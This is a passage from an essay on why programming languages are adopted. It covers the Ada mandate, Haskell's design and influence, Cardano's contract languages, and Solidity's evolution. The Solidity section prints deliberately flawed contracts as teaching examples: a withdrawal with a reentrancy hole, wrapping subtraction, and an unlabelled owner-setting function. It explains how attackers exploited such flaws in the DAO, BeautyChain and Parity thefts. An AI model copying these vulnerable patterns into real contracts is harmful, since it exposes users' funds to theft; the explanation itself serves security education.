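The National Research Council found that Ada's users were mostly in defence and in a few similar fields, such as commercial aviation and medical instruments. By one estimate, 90,000 of the 1.92 million professional programmers in the United States, or less than 5%, used Ada.

The early compilers did much to hinder Ada's adoption. Ada was hard to compile, and for several years after its release in 1980 its compilers were large, slow, unreliable and expensive. Many organisations tried Ada in the mid-1980s, rejected it and invested in something else, so they had little reason to look again when the tools improved. Makers of new microprocessors usually had a C compiler first and an Ada compiler last. Suppliers of databases and other ready-made software provided interfaces for C, often months or years before the Ada versions.

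Few universities taught Ada. A survey of more than 2,300 institutions with computer science courses found 285 that offered any Ada, including only 6 of the 53 leading American graduate programmes. The number of institutions teaching it had risen by 47% in under three years, but from a low base.

Programmers also had to consider their careers. The committee counted references to languages in job advertisements in two large newspapers. Fewer than 3% were to Ada, while C and C++ each accounted for more than 23%. An engineer at a defence firm that was laying people off could sensibly prefer to learn Java, even if Ada suited the current project better.

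These obstacles match the survey evidence on libraries and experience, and an order could do little about most of them. It could require a contractor to use Ada, but it could not make a database company support Ada promptly or a New York bank hire Ada programmers.

### The council's advice and the end of the rule

The committee advised the department to keep the rule for what it called warfighting software, such as weapon control and electronic warfare, and to drop it for software with strong commercial equivalents, such as payroll and logistics. Even for warfighting software, the rule would apply only to subsystems that were critical or had more than 10,000 lines of code.

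The Aerospace Industries Association, whose members praised Ada, wanted to end the requirement to use it and let developers choose the language. The National Research Council disagreed because the Defense Department bought its systems one at a time, so a bidder could win a contract with a cheap, fragile system and leave the cost to whoever maintained it later.

The committee also wanted the department to spend about $15 million a year on Ada tools, teaching and support, or else to end the rule entirely. To justify the figure, it considered only the upkeep of the 50 million lines of Ada already in weapon systems. It assumed that programmers changed 8% of the lines each year at $40 a line, and that better tools and more experienced staff would each reduce the cost by 8%:

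50 million × 0.08 × $40 = $160 million a year

$160 million × 0.92 × 0.92 ≈ $135 million a year

The saving of $25 million exceeds the $15 million outlay. On these assumptions, the spending breaks even if each improvement cuts costs by about 4.8%. The committee had no direct measurement of either improvement and took its estimates from general cost models, but it also used a low price per line, since general estimates for weapons software were at least $75 per line.

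Paige accepted much of the study but not the rule for weapons. In a February 1997 email, reproduced without verification in the newsgroup thread *Ada mandate cancelled*, Paige proposed removing that rule to end the resentment over the policy. The formal decision followed on 29 April, when Paige (1997), in *Use of the Ada Programming Language*, told the department to choose languages on engineering grounds, with Ada as one candidate, and abolished the waivers. Brown (1997) confirmed in *Weight of 1997-04-29 Paige Memo* that the change took effect at once.

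The department had already planned to cut its support for Ada from $10 million a year to almost nothing. Its Ada office, with a budget of about $4 million, was due to close in September 1998, according to Route Fifty's *It's curtains for the Ada Joint Program Office* (1998).

### Whether the order helped Ada

Some people in the industry thought the order had hurt Ada. Keller, a reporter on military electronics, described engineers who complained that officials were "shoving Ada down our throats" and resisted on principle. A vice president at Rational expected the end of the order to help Ada, because hostility would fade. Gwinn, in a newsgroup discussion of the decision, reported seeing the order work against adoption, and also blamed the early compilers and supporters who insisted that Ada's problems were features.

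Ada's market was partly captive. The department directed its tool funding to its own offices and contractors, and export controls applied to Ada technology for a time. Outsiders curious about the language had trouble getting a compiler. C++ and Java, by contrast, had cheap tools and enthusiastic early users in universities.

The opposing argument is that buyers undervalued Ada and only a large customer could keep it going. A department at Xerox evaluated four languages for large real-time systems and judged Ada the best in features, implementation and cost, yet the company continued to write most of that software in C and C++. The National Research Council thought commercial demand alone would not sustain good Ada tools. Some contractors did value Ada for itself, and another participant in Gwinn's discussion was using it on a defence contract that had no language requirement.

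If resentment had been the main obstacle, Ada should have gained users once the order ended. It was not among the six languages that dominated SourceForge in the following decade, though SourceForge data largely leave out Ada's main fields. The period after the order is also a poor test of resentment's effect, because the department withdrew its funding at about the same time and Java was spreading quickly. The order had never fully tested compulsion either. Ralph Crafts, an executive at an Ada vendor, told Keller that the mandate had never been enforced.

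The evidence for resentment of the order is mostly testimony, while the committee could quantify the shortage of courses and jobs. The order probably did more to build Ada's base of code, vendors and trained engineers than to drive away people who would otherwise have chosen the language. Ada's sponsors did far less to make it cheap and easy to try, though outsiders needed that more.

### Ada and SPARK in 2025 and 2026

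Ada has survived as a specialist language. The council's 1997 list of small vendors included Ada Core Technologies, which supported a free Ada compiler called GNAT. The firm, now called AdaCore, still sells Ada and SPARK tools. Ada also now has a package manager, Alire, which course notes from Loyola Marymount University compare to Rust's Cargo. With a free compiler, newcomers no longer face the high prices of the 1980s, but other languages have far more libraries and programmers.

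The most prominent recent user is the chip maker NVIDIA, which has published guidelines for using SPARK under ISO 26262, the safety standard for electronics in cars. According to slides on the personal site irvise.xyz, NVIDIA was certifying an operating system of seven million lines in Ada and SPARK in 2025. The exact claim needs some caution because the slides give the safety level as SIL-4, which belongs to a different standard. ISO 26262 grades systems from A to D.

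NVIDIA is a commercial company under no order to use Ada, but its work on cars has the strict safety requirements that the council associated with Ada's niche. US agencies returned to the subject of programming languages in the 2020s with advice on memory safety.

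## Haskell, a pure language with few users and wide influence

The university researchers who designed Haskell gave it away and could only persuade people to use it, whereas the Defense Department could order contractors to use Ada. They built Haskell on the principle that a function computes a result and does nothing else. Few programmers adopted the language, but many now use ideas from it in other languages.

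### Types that separate computing from acting

A Haskell programmer can usually tell from a function's type whether it can perform input or output. Peyton Jones (2017), in *Escape from the ivory tower*, a talk by one of the language's designers, gives these examples:

```haskell
toUpper :: Char -> Char
getChar :: IO Char
putChar :: Char -> IO ()
```

The double colon means "has the type". `toUpper` takes a character and returns a character, so it cannot print anything or read a file. `getChar` is an action. When the program performs it, the action may do input or output before delivering a character. `putChar` takes a character and returns an action that delivers only an empty value, written `()`.

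`Char` and `IO Char` are different types, so the compiler rejects `toUpper getChar`. `toUpper` needs a character, and `getChar` is only an action that would fetch one. The programmer has to write a new action instead:

```haskell
shout :: IO ()
shout = do
  c <- getChar
  putChar (toUpper c)
```

The arrow gives the name `c` to the character that `getChar` reads. Joining two actions always produces another action, so any input or output inside a computation appears in its type.

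*A History of Haskell* (Hudak, Hughes and colleagues, 2007) points out that if a function `f` has the type `Int -> Int`, every call `f 3` returns the same value. The function cannot depend on a variable that other code has changed, and it cannot overwrite a file. It also cannot send data over a network, which is why some researchers want the same guarantee for code that AI agents write.

But `toUpper` could still return the wrong letter, and a pure function can crash, run forever or use up the computer's memory. Printing a character and deleting a folder can both have the type `IO ()`, so the type shows that code can act but not what it will do. Haskell also provides `unsafePerformIO`, which runs an action inside a function whose type looks pure.

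The separation also makes some simple changes laborious. Suppose a programmer wants `toUpper` to record each call in a log file. In Java this takes one extra line, but in Haskell the type of `toUpper` becomes `Char -> IO Char`, and the functions that call `toUpper`, directly or indirectly, must become actions too.

### Why the designers did not compromise

Haskell uses lazy evaluation, so a program computes a value only when something needs it. Peyton Jones uses the list `[print "yes", print "no"]` to show why this fits badly with ordinary printing. If `print` wrote to the screen as soon as the program evaluated it, as it does in most languages, code that only counted the items in the list would print nothing, because counting does not require their values. Code that evaluated the second item first would print "no" before "yes".

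Most languages evaluate a function's arguments before calling it, so effects happen in a predictable order. Hudak and colleagues describe the temptation to allow unrestricted effects in such languages as "almost irresistible". Haskell is lazy, meaning that it evaluates an argument only when its value is needed, and this makes effects inside functions nearly useless. Haskell's designers therefore had to find another way to do input and output. They later thought that keeping the language pure was perhaps the biggest benefit of laziness. But laziness also makes a program's memory use hard to predict, even for experienced programmers.

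Hudak and colleagues call Haskell's early input and output "painfully clumsy" and a source of considerable embarrassment. In one design, the whole program was a function that received a list of responses from the operating system and produced a list of requests. Laziness let the program issue a request before the response to it existed, but the programmer had to keep the two lists synchronized. In another design, each operation took the function to run next as an argument.

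The `IO` type entered the official definition of Haskell in May 1996, six years after the first version. The designers called the pattern for joining actions a monad, a term from mathematics. Peyton Jones jokes that their biggest mistake was using this scary word instead of "warm fuzzy thing". The name may well have put people off, since the students surveyed by Meyerovich and Rabkin liked interfaces far better than static types.

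### The committee and its first rival

By September 1987 there were more than a dozen lazy, pure languages. They were similar in power, and almost all had users at only one site. That month a group of researchers at a conference in Portland, Oregon, agreed that the lack of a common language was holding back wider use of such languages, and set up a committee to design one for teaching, research and large applications.

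The committee first asked David Turner for permission to build on Miranda, the most mature of these languages, which was running at 120 sites. Turner declined because he wanted a single standard without dialects. The committee therefore had to settle every detail itself, but it was also free to try more radical ideas. It published the first definition of Haskell on 1 April 1990.

By the early 1990s, 250 universities and about 50 companies had Miranda, yet Haskell largely replaced it. Hudak and colleagues attribute this mainly to economics. Turner's small company sold licences and had no Windows version, while publicly funded universities gave Haskell away and improved its compilers faster. The two languages looked and behaved much alike, so Miranda users could switch easily, whereas C programmers had much more to give up.

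### "Avoid success at all costs"

Haskell's unofficial motto, "avoid success at all costs", can be read in two ways. If "at all costs" goes with "avoid", designers should shun popularity. If it goes with "success", they may welcome users but should not sacrifice the language's principles to get them. The dollar sign in the title of a Haskell forum thread, *What does (Avoid $ Success At All Costs) mean to you?*, is a joke in favour of the second reading, because in Haskell the sign groups everything after it, as if in brackets.

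Haskell's designers have also defended something close to the first reading. Hudak and colleagues call it "an accidental virtue" that Haskell had not become too successful. They argue that Java had so many users that standards, user groups and old code bogged it down, while Haskell's small community welcomed changes. Peyton Jones similarly says that Haskell has enough users to drive innovation but too few to stifle it.

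The 1996 change to input and output is consistent with this. It affected one of the most basic parts of the language, and would have been much harder with millions of lines of commercial code to convert. But even a small community soon wanted stability. One user complained that it was impossible to write a book about a language that kept changing. The committee responded with Haskell 98, which compiler writers promised to support indefinitely, while others remained free to experiment with extensions.

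The forum thread describes a more recent conflict over a change to type checking, called simplified subsumption, that broke a lot of existing code. Companies and others using Haskell in production protested, and GHC, the main compiler, gained an option to restore the old behaviour.

Haskell's own designers argued for staying small, but they did so after the language had failed to become popular. In 1987 they had wanted pure languages to spread. Having few users made Haskell easier to change, but the committee does not seem to have planned to keep the user base small.

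### Wadler's reasons

Wadler, another of the designers, listed the obstacles facing functional languages in general, including ML and Erlang, in his 1998 column *Why no one uses functional languages*. Some experiments showed that programmers were four times as productive in these languages, yet almost everyone at Bell Labs, where Wadler worked, used C or C++.

Many systems combined existing components written in C or C++, and functional languages did not always connect to them easily. Lazy languages had particular trouble because their order of evaluation is hard to predict, which also hindered the development of debuggers. Libraries were scarce, and one typical user called installing the main Haskell compiler an "adventure".

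Wadler also described career risks. A manager whose project failed in C++ could point out that everyone else had such failures, but a manager who had chosen a functional language would be fired. At the telecommunications company Lucent, no developer would take over an important tool written in Standard ML, so the company eventually hired a physicist who wanted to change fields.

Wadler listed unfamiliarity as an obstacle, but thought training could overcome it. A German company, Software AG, taught industrial programmers a functional language, including lazy evaluation, in a one-week course. The students were annoyed when the compiler kept rejecting their programs, then pleasantly surprised when the programs ran correctly at the first attempt. Programmers usually miss this benefit of types in a short trial, but these students saw it within a week.

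Wadler rejected two popular explanations for why few people used functional languages. The first was that programs ran slowly, but Perl and Visual Basic had succeeded despite being slow. The second was that programmers failed to appreciate functional programming, but Wadler quoted a commercial developer who admired Haskell's elegance and still needed documentation and stability. Wadler's remedy was a "killer app", something useful that is hard to do in any other language. In Coburn's terms, Wadler's obstacles are the pain of adoption, and a killer app addresses a crisis that users already feel.

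The column is an insider's judgement, but Meyerovich and Rabkin's later survey, in which libraries and existing code ranked highest, supports much of it.

### What other languages borrowed

Programmers can use many of Haskell's ideas without adopting Haskell. Type classes are one example. In the 1980s, a programmer who defined a squaring function in Standard ML needed a separate version for each type of number. Miranda avoided this by having only one numeric type, but its compiler then accepted `mod 8 3.4`, although remainders normally make sense only for whole numbers. Wadler proposed a more general solution to the Haskell committee in 1988:

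```haskell
square :: Num a => a -> a
square x = x * x
```

The first line means that `square` works for any type `a` that belongs to the class `Num`. The class lists operations such as addition and multiplication, and programmers define these operations for each type they add to the class. The compiler passes `square` a hidden table of the operations for `a`. Rust's traits use much the same idea.

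Microsoft's language C# acquired another of these ideas through LINQ, a notation for querying data. Erik Meijer, one of its main designers, said that Haskell's monad comprehensions directly inspired it. These extend Haskell's notation for building lists to other structures. The first line below is Haskell and the second is C#:

```text
[name p | p <- people, age p > 65]
from p in people where p.Age > 65 select p.Name
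```

Both produce the names of people over 65. The C# version resembles SQL, the standard database language, so its notation was already familiar to many business programmers. Haskell's 1997 definition included monad comprehensions, but two years later the language again limited comprehensions to lists.

Explicit optional values have also spread to other languages. A Haskell value of type `Maybe Int` is either `Nothing` or a number marked with `Just`, as in `Just 5`. The compiler rejects code that adds 1 to it directly, so the programmer has to handle the case where the number is missing. Haskell popularised this technique, but Hudak and colleagues trace the kind of type behind it to an earlier language called Hope. Rust has a similar type called `Option`, and Java has `Optional`.

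These features lost some of their guarantees in languages without Haskell's other rules. A Java variable of type `Optional` can itself be null, meaning it holds nothing, and using it then causes the crash that the type should prevent. C# evaluates many LINQ queries lazily but does not require the code inside them to be pure. If the `where` condition above also printed each name, nothing would appear until other code read the results, and the names would appear again on every read. Haskell's designers kept effects out of functions because of this problem.

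Meijer came to believe that partly removing side effects cannot make an ordinary language safer, because the remaining effects can often simulate the ones removed. CowboyRobot quotes this view in *Erik Meijer*, a post on the news site Slashdot. The argument is persuasive for guarantees about effects, but it does not apply to everything that languages borrowed from Haskell. Optional values, for example, catch many missing-value errors even in code full of side effects.

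Peyton Jones seems content with the exchange and says that the ideas matter more than the language. In 2017 he estimated that GHC had well over 100,000 users, and he counted more than 11,000 packages in Haskell's public library. Haskell therefore has a working community, though it is small compared with those of the major languages.

### Cardano and the move to Aiken

One current industrial user of Haskell is Cardano, a blockchain, which is a ledger shared by many computers. According to Aiken's website, the current node software, which each of those computers runs, is written in Haskell. Cardano also runs smart contracts, which are programs stored on a blockchain that hold and move assets by their own rules. When Cardano introduced them in 2021, developers wrote them mainly in Plutus, a language based on Haskell and now called Plinth.

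A pure language suits Cardano contracts because a contract only receives the details of a proposed transaction and returns yes or no. Every contract language on Cardano compiles to the same low-level language, so developers can change languages without leaving the platform.

The *Aiken* proposal, from the small company TxPipe, sought funding for a new language because most developers found Haskell's notation "unpalatable or too unfamiliar". TxPipe wrote that "most developers are used to curly braces." Aiken has braces and looks somewhat like Rust. Its designers changed Haskell's notation and tools but kept its purity and static types. In Aiken's sample contract, the line `expect Some(Datum { owner }) = datum` handles an optional value, and the contract approves the transaction only if the owner has signed it and it contains the right greeting.

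The Cardano Foundation, which supports the blockchain's development, surveys Cardano developers. Cexplorer's *State of the Cardano Developer Ecosystem* compares the first two surveys. In 2022, 389 people responded, and Plutus ranked first for writing contracts, followed by Marlowe, a language for financial contracts. In 2023, 174 people responded, and Aiken ranked first, followed by Haskell. Respondents named Haskell as a major difficulty in both years. By 2025, more than 75% of 109 respondents, or at least 82 people, used Aiken, according to Benkort's *State of the Cardano Developer Ecosystem Survey* (2025). The platform had about 670 active developers in 2024.

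The surveys do not show how many people moved from Plutus to Aiken. They did not follow the same developers, and some of the 82 may never have used Plutus or may use both. The number of respondents with more than ten years of functional programming experience rose from 10 in 2022 (under 3%) to 43 in 2023 (about 25%), so different groups must have answered. Because Aiken came first in the sample with far more of these experienced programmers, a lack of functional programming experience is a less likely explanation for its lead.

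The 2023 result may also reflect developers' intentions more than their actual use. Lido Nation's *The Heartbeat of Cardano Shifts to Aiken ♥* describes the question as asking which language developers intended to use, and the Foundation was still advising against using Aiken in production that April. The Foundation also has an interest in the results, because it funds Aiken, and Benkort, who reported the 2025 survey, leads the language's development. Even so, the 2025 figure is high enough that Aiken's lead among respondents is fairly clear.

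Braces are only one possible reason for it. Rosa (2023), in *Aiken*, a launch article by a founder of the language, complains that Plutus took days to set up and that its editor tools often failed. Plutus also looked like standard Haskell but behaved differently, which confused even experienced Haskell programmers. The Cardano Developer Portal's *Choose a Smart Contract Language* adds that Aiken compiles in seconds and has built-in tests, while Plutus has long build times and cryptic errors. Plutus contracts are also larger. Users pay for the computing steps and memory a contract uses, and a contract that exceeds the limit cannot run at all, so an inefficient compiler raises users' fees or makes some designs impossible.

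Cardano's other languages offer a rough way to separate these causes. Czeladka (2026), in *Building on Cardano Without Haskell*, rated seven of them for the Foundation, including these five:

| Language | Notation | Closeness to mainstream languages | Difficulty for outsiders | Performance |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plutus (Plinth) | Haskell | Low | High | Contracts use more resources |
| Plutarch | Haskell | Very low | High | Strong |
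| Aiken | Its own, with braces | High | Low | Excellent |
| Helios | Similar to JavaScript | Very high | Low | Strong, but below Aiken |
| OpShin | Python | Very high | Low | No published benchmarks |

Aiken combines fairly familiar notation with efficient contracts and good tools. It also has funding from the Foundation, and it was available before Helios and OpShin appeared in the surveys, so the effect of each advantage cannot be separated in this comparison. Neither familiar notation nor performance alone explains Aiken's lead, since Helios and OpShin have more familiar notation, and Plutarch's performance did not keep more developers on Haskell. Czeladka believes that developers generally put performance and stable maintenance ahead of convenient syntax.

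Czeladka thinks the hardest part for newcomers is often Cardano's way of recording transactions, which differs from the account balances used on Ethereum, the blockchain Solidity was designed for. A Python programmer can read an OpShin contract on the first day and still not know how to divide an application into Cardano transactions.

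## Solidity, familiar syntax on an unfamiliar machine

Ethereum's designers chose familiar notation from the start, whereas Cardano began with a Haskell-based contract language and got more familiar ones later. Ethereum is a blockchain whose computers all run the same contracts on a common virtual machine, the EVM, and its currency is called ether. Users pay a fee, called gas, for each step a contract takes. Nobody can normally change a contract's code once it is on the blockchain, so a mistake in the code remains and continues to put money at risk.

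### What the designers intended

Gavin Wood, a co-founder of Ethereum, proposed Solidity in 2014, and Christian Reitwiessner led much of the early work on its compiler. They presented the language in *Solidity, Vision and Roadmap* at Ethereum's first developer conference late that year. In the transcript in Early Days of Ethereum's *ethereum devcon-0*, Wood's two main concerns are that lots of people should be able to write contracts and that the contracts should be correct.

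Wood expected many of those people to know web technologies already, so giving the language a syntax like JavaScript's would "leverage the existing skill set". Wood showed one piece of notation that looked too much like C and invited the audience to suggest something "slightly more JavaScripty".

For correctness, Wood relied on tests and on proofs that the compiler would check. One example was a currency contract with a rule that all balances always add up to a billion. The compiler would prove that no function could break the rule, so users could trust it without reading the code.

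Recruiting web developers was therefore a stated aim from the start, but some later accounts treat it as the only one. In a Hacker News discussion, avaer called Solidity "a marketing tool" for bringing people to Ethereum, and vog thought a platform for security-sensitive code should have tried to attract Haskell and Rust programmers. Wood's talk covered proofs at least as fully as syntax, so it doesn't support the view that safety was an afterthought. However, the proofs were still only planned when the syntax was already working.

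Solidity's developers later gave a similar account in *The Road to Core Solidity* (2025). They wrote that they focused early on ergonomics and good abstractions, and that familiarity was also important. Safety always mattered to them, but it "only gradually" came to override other goals, as repeated thefts exposed weaknesses.

JavaScript also influenced Solidity's design less than its reputation suggests. Reitwiessner remarked in 2014 that adding types to JavaScript produces something close to C or C++. *Language Influences*, in Solidity's official documentation, names C++ as the deepest influence, visible in variable declarations, loops and type conversions. Python was the model for multiple inheritance and for modifiers, which wrap a function in extra checks. Early Solidity borrowed JavaScript's `var` keyword and its rules for where a variable is visible, but the developers reduced that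 influence from version 0.4.0 onwards, leaving the word `function` as the main similarity. Thoughtworks (2018) still described the syntax as similar to JavaScript's.

### How a withdrawal can run twice

The following contract keeps ether for its users. It would look unremarkable to a programmer who knows JavaScript or C++:

```solidity
contract Bank {
    mapping(address => uint) balances;

    function deposit() public payable {
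        balances[msg.sender] += msg.value;
    }

    function withdraw() public {
        uint amount = balances[msg.sender];
        (bool ok, ) = msg.sender.call{value: amount}("");
        require(ok);
        balances[msg.sender] = 0;
    }
}
```

`msg.sender` is the account that called the function. `withdraw` looks up the caller's balance, sends that much ether, checks that the payment went through, and then sets the balance to zero.

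These steps are in the wrong order. On Ethereum, the recipient of a payment can itself be a contract, and sending it ether in this way also runs its code. `withdraw` pauses until that code finishes. If the code calls `withdraw` again, the second call reads a balance that the first has not yet reduced. Programmers call this reentrancy.

Suppose the contract holds 30 ether, of which 10 belong to an attacker and 20 to other people.

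| Step | Attacker's recorded balance | Ether in the contract | Ether paid to the attacker |
|---|---|---|---|
| Before the attack | 10 | 30 | 0 |
| The first call to `withdraw` sends 10 | 10 | 20 | 10 |
| The attacker's code calls `withdraw` again, which sends 10 more | 10 | 10 | 20 |
| The second call finishes and sets the balance to 0 | 0 | 10 | 20 |
| The first call finishes and sets the balance to 0 again | 0 | 10 | 20 |

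The attacker has withdrawn 20 ether from a balance of 10. The contract can now repay only half of what it owes everyone else, and one more call would have emptied it.

Moving the last line of `withdraw` above the payment fixes the bug, because the balance is then already zero when a second call arrives. Programmers can also set a lock, usually with a modifier, that blocks further calls from when the function starts until it ends. The Solidity compiler accepts the faulty version as well as both fixed ones.

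Reentrancy is also possible in JavaScript, whenever a function runs a callback before it has finished updating its data, but the programmer can usually see the callback. In Solidity, the dangerous line looks like a payment, and it may run code belonging to an attacker who is trying to steal the money.

### The DAO

In 2016 an investment fund called The DAO ran entirely as a contract on Ethereum. It had raised ether worth about $150 million from thousands of people, who would vote on how to invest it. A member who disagreed could split off and take a share of the money into a new fund. Like `withdraw` above, the code for splitting paid out a reward before it reduced the member's balance.

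On 17 June 2016 an attacker used this flaw to take about 3.6 million ether, nearly a third of the fund, then worth between $50 million and $60 million. The DAO's rules kept the ether in the attacker's new fund for several weeks, which gave others time to debate how to respond.

Some people held that the code was the contract and that the attacker had only used it as written. Most of the network disagreed, and on 20 July it adopted a rule change that moved the ether to a contract from which investors could reclaim it. A minority refused the change and continued the old blockchain, now called Ethereum Classic, where the theft was never reversed. Two steps in the wrong order had led to the split, and few later victims could hope for the same rescue.

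### Wrapped numbers and open functions

Solidity's usual number type, `uint`, holds whole numbers from 0 to 2²⁵⁶ − 1. Before version 0.8, a result outside that range wrapped around without an error, like a car's mileage counter returning to zero. Reitwiessner said in the 2014 talk that "the type system ignores overflow" when code adds 200 and 200 as 8-bit numbers, which go up to 255. The result would be 144.

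An early page of Ethereum's wiki, *Solidity*, contains a deliberate mistake of this kind. Its example currency has a function for sending coins:

```solidity
balances[to] += valueInmGAV;
balances[transaction.sender] -= valueInmGAV;
```

If someone with 5 coins sends 8, the sender's balance wraps to 2²⁵⁶ − 3, a 78-digit number, instead of becoming −3. Solidity is familiar mainly because it resembles JavaScript and C++, but programmers who know those languages would expect different results here. A JavaScript programmer would expect −3, while a C++ programmer would know that unsigned numbers wrap.

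According to the wiki page, the compiler would reject any subtraction that might wrap unless the programmer had explicitly allowed it. Solidity as people used it in its first years had no such check. The wiki's other protection, a rule fixing the total number of coins, would not necessarily have helped. The sender's balance falls by 8 and the recipient's rises by 8, so the total would still be correct if the checker added the balances with the same wrapping arithmetic.

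In April 2018 an attacker exploited a multiplication overflow in a token called BeautyChain. Its function for paying several people at once multiplied the number of recipients by the amount for each, then checked that the sender's balance covered the product. The attacker named two recipients and an amount of 2²⁵⁵. The product, 2²⁵⁶, wrapped to zero, so the check passed. Each recipient received the full amount, and exchanges suspended trading.

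Visibility, meaning who may call a function, was another trap. In a C++ class, a function with no label is private. In Solidity before version 0.5 it was public, so a programmer could write this as an internal helper and leave it open to everyone:

```solidity
function setOwner(address newOwner) { owner = newOwner; }
```

Anyone could then make themselves the owner. Even the keyword `private` can mislead, because it stops other contracts from reading a variable, but people can still read everything on a public blockchain.

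The best-known case of an open function is the July 2017 theft of about 150,000 ether, then worth some $30 million, from wallets made by the company Parity. The function that set a wallet's owners had no visibility label, and thieves called it on wallets already in use. Requiring a label would probably not have prevented the theft, because each new wallet had to call this function in another contract, so the correct label was `public`. The code lacked a check that the wallet had no owner yet.

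### What the repairs broke

Version 0.5, released in November 2018, required programmers to state the visibility of every function. Old source code would not compile until someone added the labels. Adding `public` everywhere was tedious but easy, and it restored the old behaviour, including its risks. The same version removed `var` and the C++ convention of naming a constructor, the function that sets up a new contract, after the contract itself. The developers of one contract had renamed it Rubixi without renaming its constructor, which became an ordinary public function that let anyone take ownership of the contract.

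Version 0.8 followed in December 2020 and made arithmetic fail when a result doesn't fit. A failure cancels the whole transaction, so the wiki's 5-coin sender would keep the 5 coins. Many projects had been using the SafeMath library for the same purpose and could now drop it. To get the old behaviour, programmers must put the calculation in a block marked `unchecked`.

Unlike the visibility rule, this change affected code that still compiled. For example, version 2 of the exchange Uniswap keeps a running total of each price multiplied by the seconds it lasted, and other contracts compute an average price from the difference between two readings. The total is meant to wrap. With a counter that goes up to 255, a reading of 250 followed by an increase of 10 gives 4, and the wrapped result of 4 − 250 is again 10. Under checked arithmetic, the addition would fail instead, and the pool would stop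 trading. RareSkills' *Build Your Own Uniswap*, a guide to rewriting the exchange in modern Solidity, therefore tells programmers to put `unchecked` around this code. Zealynx's course on Uniswap version 3 does the same for every intended overflow.

Checked arithmetic also happens to stop some reentrancy attacks. If the last line of `withdraw` were `balances[msg.sender] -= amount`, the first call would try to subtract 10 from 0 after the second had finished. Since Solidity 0.8, that subtraction fails and cancels both payments. If the last line sets the balance to zero instead, the code still compiles and the contract loses the money.

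Solidity's developers have never made reentrancy an error. For years, many programmers relied on the functions `send` and `transfer` to prevent it, because they give the recipient too little gas to do much. Ethereum later changed how much gas operations use, which made any fixed allowance unreliable. The Solidity team has deprecated both functions and plans to remove them in version 0.9.

These repairs were unusually easy for a popular language because contracts on the blockchain are already compiled and can call contracts written in other versions. A new compiler therefore breaks nothing that is running, and programmers need to adapt only the source code they want to reuse. Solidity thus avoided the problem Haskell's designers had feared for their own language, that having many users would make it impossible to change. The *Solidity Developer Survey 2025*, which ran in February and March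 2026, found 86% of respondents using version 0.8 and no more than 8% using any one of the older series.

For the same reason, the repairs don't help contracts that are already deployed. Uniswap's second version was written for compiler 0.5.16, as *Uniswap v2 annotated code* shows, so it has to get its arithmetic checks from a library. According to Hacken's *Uniswap V2 Core Contracts*, this version still holds about 40% of the assets in Uniswap. It has been safe so far because its developers were careful, not because of any later version of Solidity.

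The proofs that Wood promised in 2014 exist in some form. The Solidity compiler includes the SMTChecker, which tries to prove that a contract can never violate conditions its author has written. In the same survey, 45% of respondents had never heard of it and only 7% used it often. In *Type safety for Isabelle/Solidity*, Thornton and Marmsoler (2026) used a proof assistant to prove that programs in their formal model of Solidity keep stored data consistent with its types. Their proof covers errors that confuse one kind of data with another, but not the kind of error that emptied The DAO.

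### Losses a language could have prevented

Hacken, a security company, counted 44 incidents and $482 million in losses in the blockchain industry in the first quarter of 2026. That total says little about programming languages until it is divided by cause, because thieves often don't need a faulty contract. Some large cases from recent years give a sense of the range:

| Incident | What went wrong | Approximate loss | Language feature that could have helped |
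|---|---|---|---|
| Bybit, 2025 | Staff approved a transaction that a tampered web page had disguised | $1.5 billion | None |
| Ronin, 2022 | Thieves obtained the keys that approved transfers | $620 million | None |
| Euler, 2023 | A function did not check whether a borrower could still repay | $197 million | Proof against a written rule |
| Balancer, 2025 | Rounding errors added up over many small trades | Over $100 million | Proof against a written rule |
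| GMX, 2025 | Reentrancy | $42 million, mostly returned | A ban on unsafe re-entry |

Bybit alone lost about three times as much as the losses Hacken counted for the whole industry in a quarter. No compiler could have detected that the page its staff were looking at showed false information.

A stricter language would have helped with Euler and Balancer only if someone had thought to write down the rule that the code broke. The Euler function ran exactly as written, and, as with the Ariane 5 software, a checker could not have supplied the condition that everyone forgot.

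The list is too short to support a percentage, and its thefts were chosen by size. It also understates how much languages can prevent, since it leaves out thefts that no longer happen. Attacks like the one on BeautyChain were a serious worry in 2018, but a contract compiled today with ordinary arithmetic is immune to them. Reentrancy, which the compiler still allows, was costing tens of millions of dollars nine years after The DAO. So a better language could probably have prevented a minority of the financial losses in recent years, but a fairly large share of the mistakes programmers make in individual lines of code.

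### Core Solidity

The team behind Solidity now wants to replace much of the language. Around 25 employees of the Ethereum Foundation, which had paid for Solidity's development, formed the non-profit Argot Collective and moved the project there. Their redesign, Core Solidity, has a new type system that borrows from Haskell and Rust. The present language is now called "Classic Solidity".

Solidity's *Pattern Matching in Core Solidity* (2026) explains one benefit with a contract that handles three kinds of payment. In Classic Solidity, a function that calculates fees tests for each kind in turn and ends with `return 0`, a line that should never run but that the compiler requires. If a programmer adds a fourth kind of payment and forgets this function, the contract charges those customers nothing. Core Solidity lets the programmer list the possibilities as a type, as in this simplified version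 of the example:

```text
data Payment =
    Ether(address, word)
  | Token(address, address, word)
  | Collectible(address, address, tokenid);
```

Each kind of payment carries only the data it needs, so a payment in plain ether can't also contain a collectible token's number. If a function that handles payments omits a kind, the compiler rejects it and reports a missing case. The check adds nothing to the running contract, so it costs no gas.

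The team expects auditors to stop looking for such omissions, which is too optimistic because programmers may end the list of cases with a wildcard that covers everything else. The team's own example of a discount function ends with one that returns 0. A new kind added later would match the wildcard without causing an error, just as in Classic Solidity.

None of this prevents reentrancy. Linear types might, by requiring a program to use a value exactly once, so that code could not spend the same claim to 10 ether twice. Solidity's *Core Solidity Deep Dive* (2025) calls them well suited to the accounting rules that contracts need, but defers them until some time after the first release.

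The designers are again counting on familiarity. They intend to match the existing syntax closely and let projects mix both languages. But they will remove inheritance, which lets one contract build on another's code. Of those who answered the survey's question on language features, 54% chose contracts as objects and inheritance as important. Of the respondents who knew about Core Solidity, 63% said losing inheritance would cause them difficulties. One feared an "academic Haskell language that requires a PhD in types". In the talk *From Classic to Core Solidity*, team member Sliwak warned of a repeat of Python's move to version 3, which took about a decade.

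That decision is still some way off. Argot Collective's reference manual describes the software as a research prototype that contains bugs, and the team has not committed to a release date. In June 2026 a developer reported in the forum thread *Core Solidity* that Uniswap's main version 2 contract compiled in it, and found the language further along than expected. The developer also asked for checked arithmetic by default and for modifiers to guard against reentrancy. Most Solidity programmers have not formed an opinion, because 70% of those surveyed did not know what Core Solidity was. Solidity's summary of the survey (2026) calls this a "visibility and communication problem".

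### Why Solidity kept its lead

The Solidity team calls its language the most widely used for smart contracts and says that it secures hundreds of billions of dollars. Thornton and Marmsoler also call it the most popular. Programmers have kept using it despite thefts, some of them famous, from contracts written in it.

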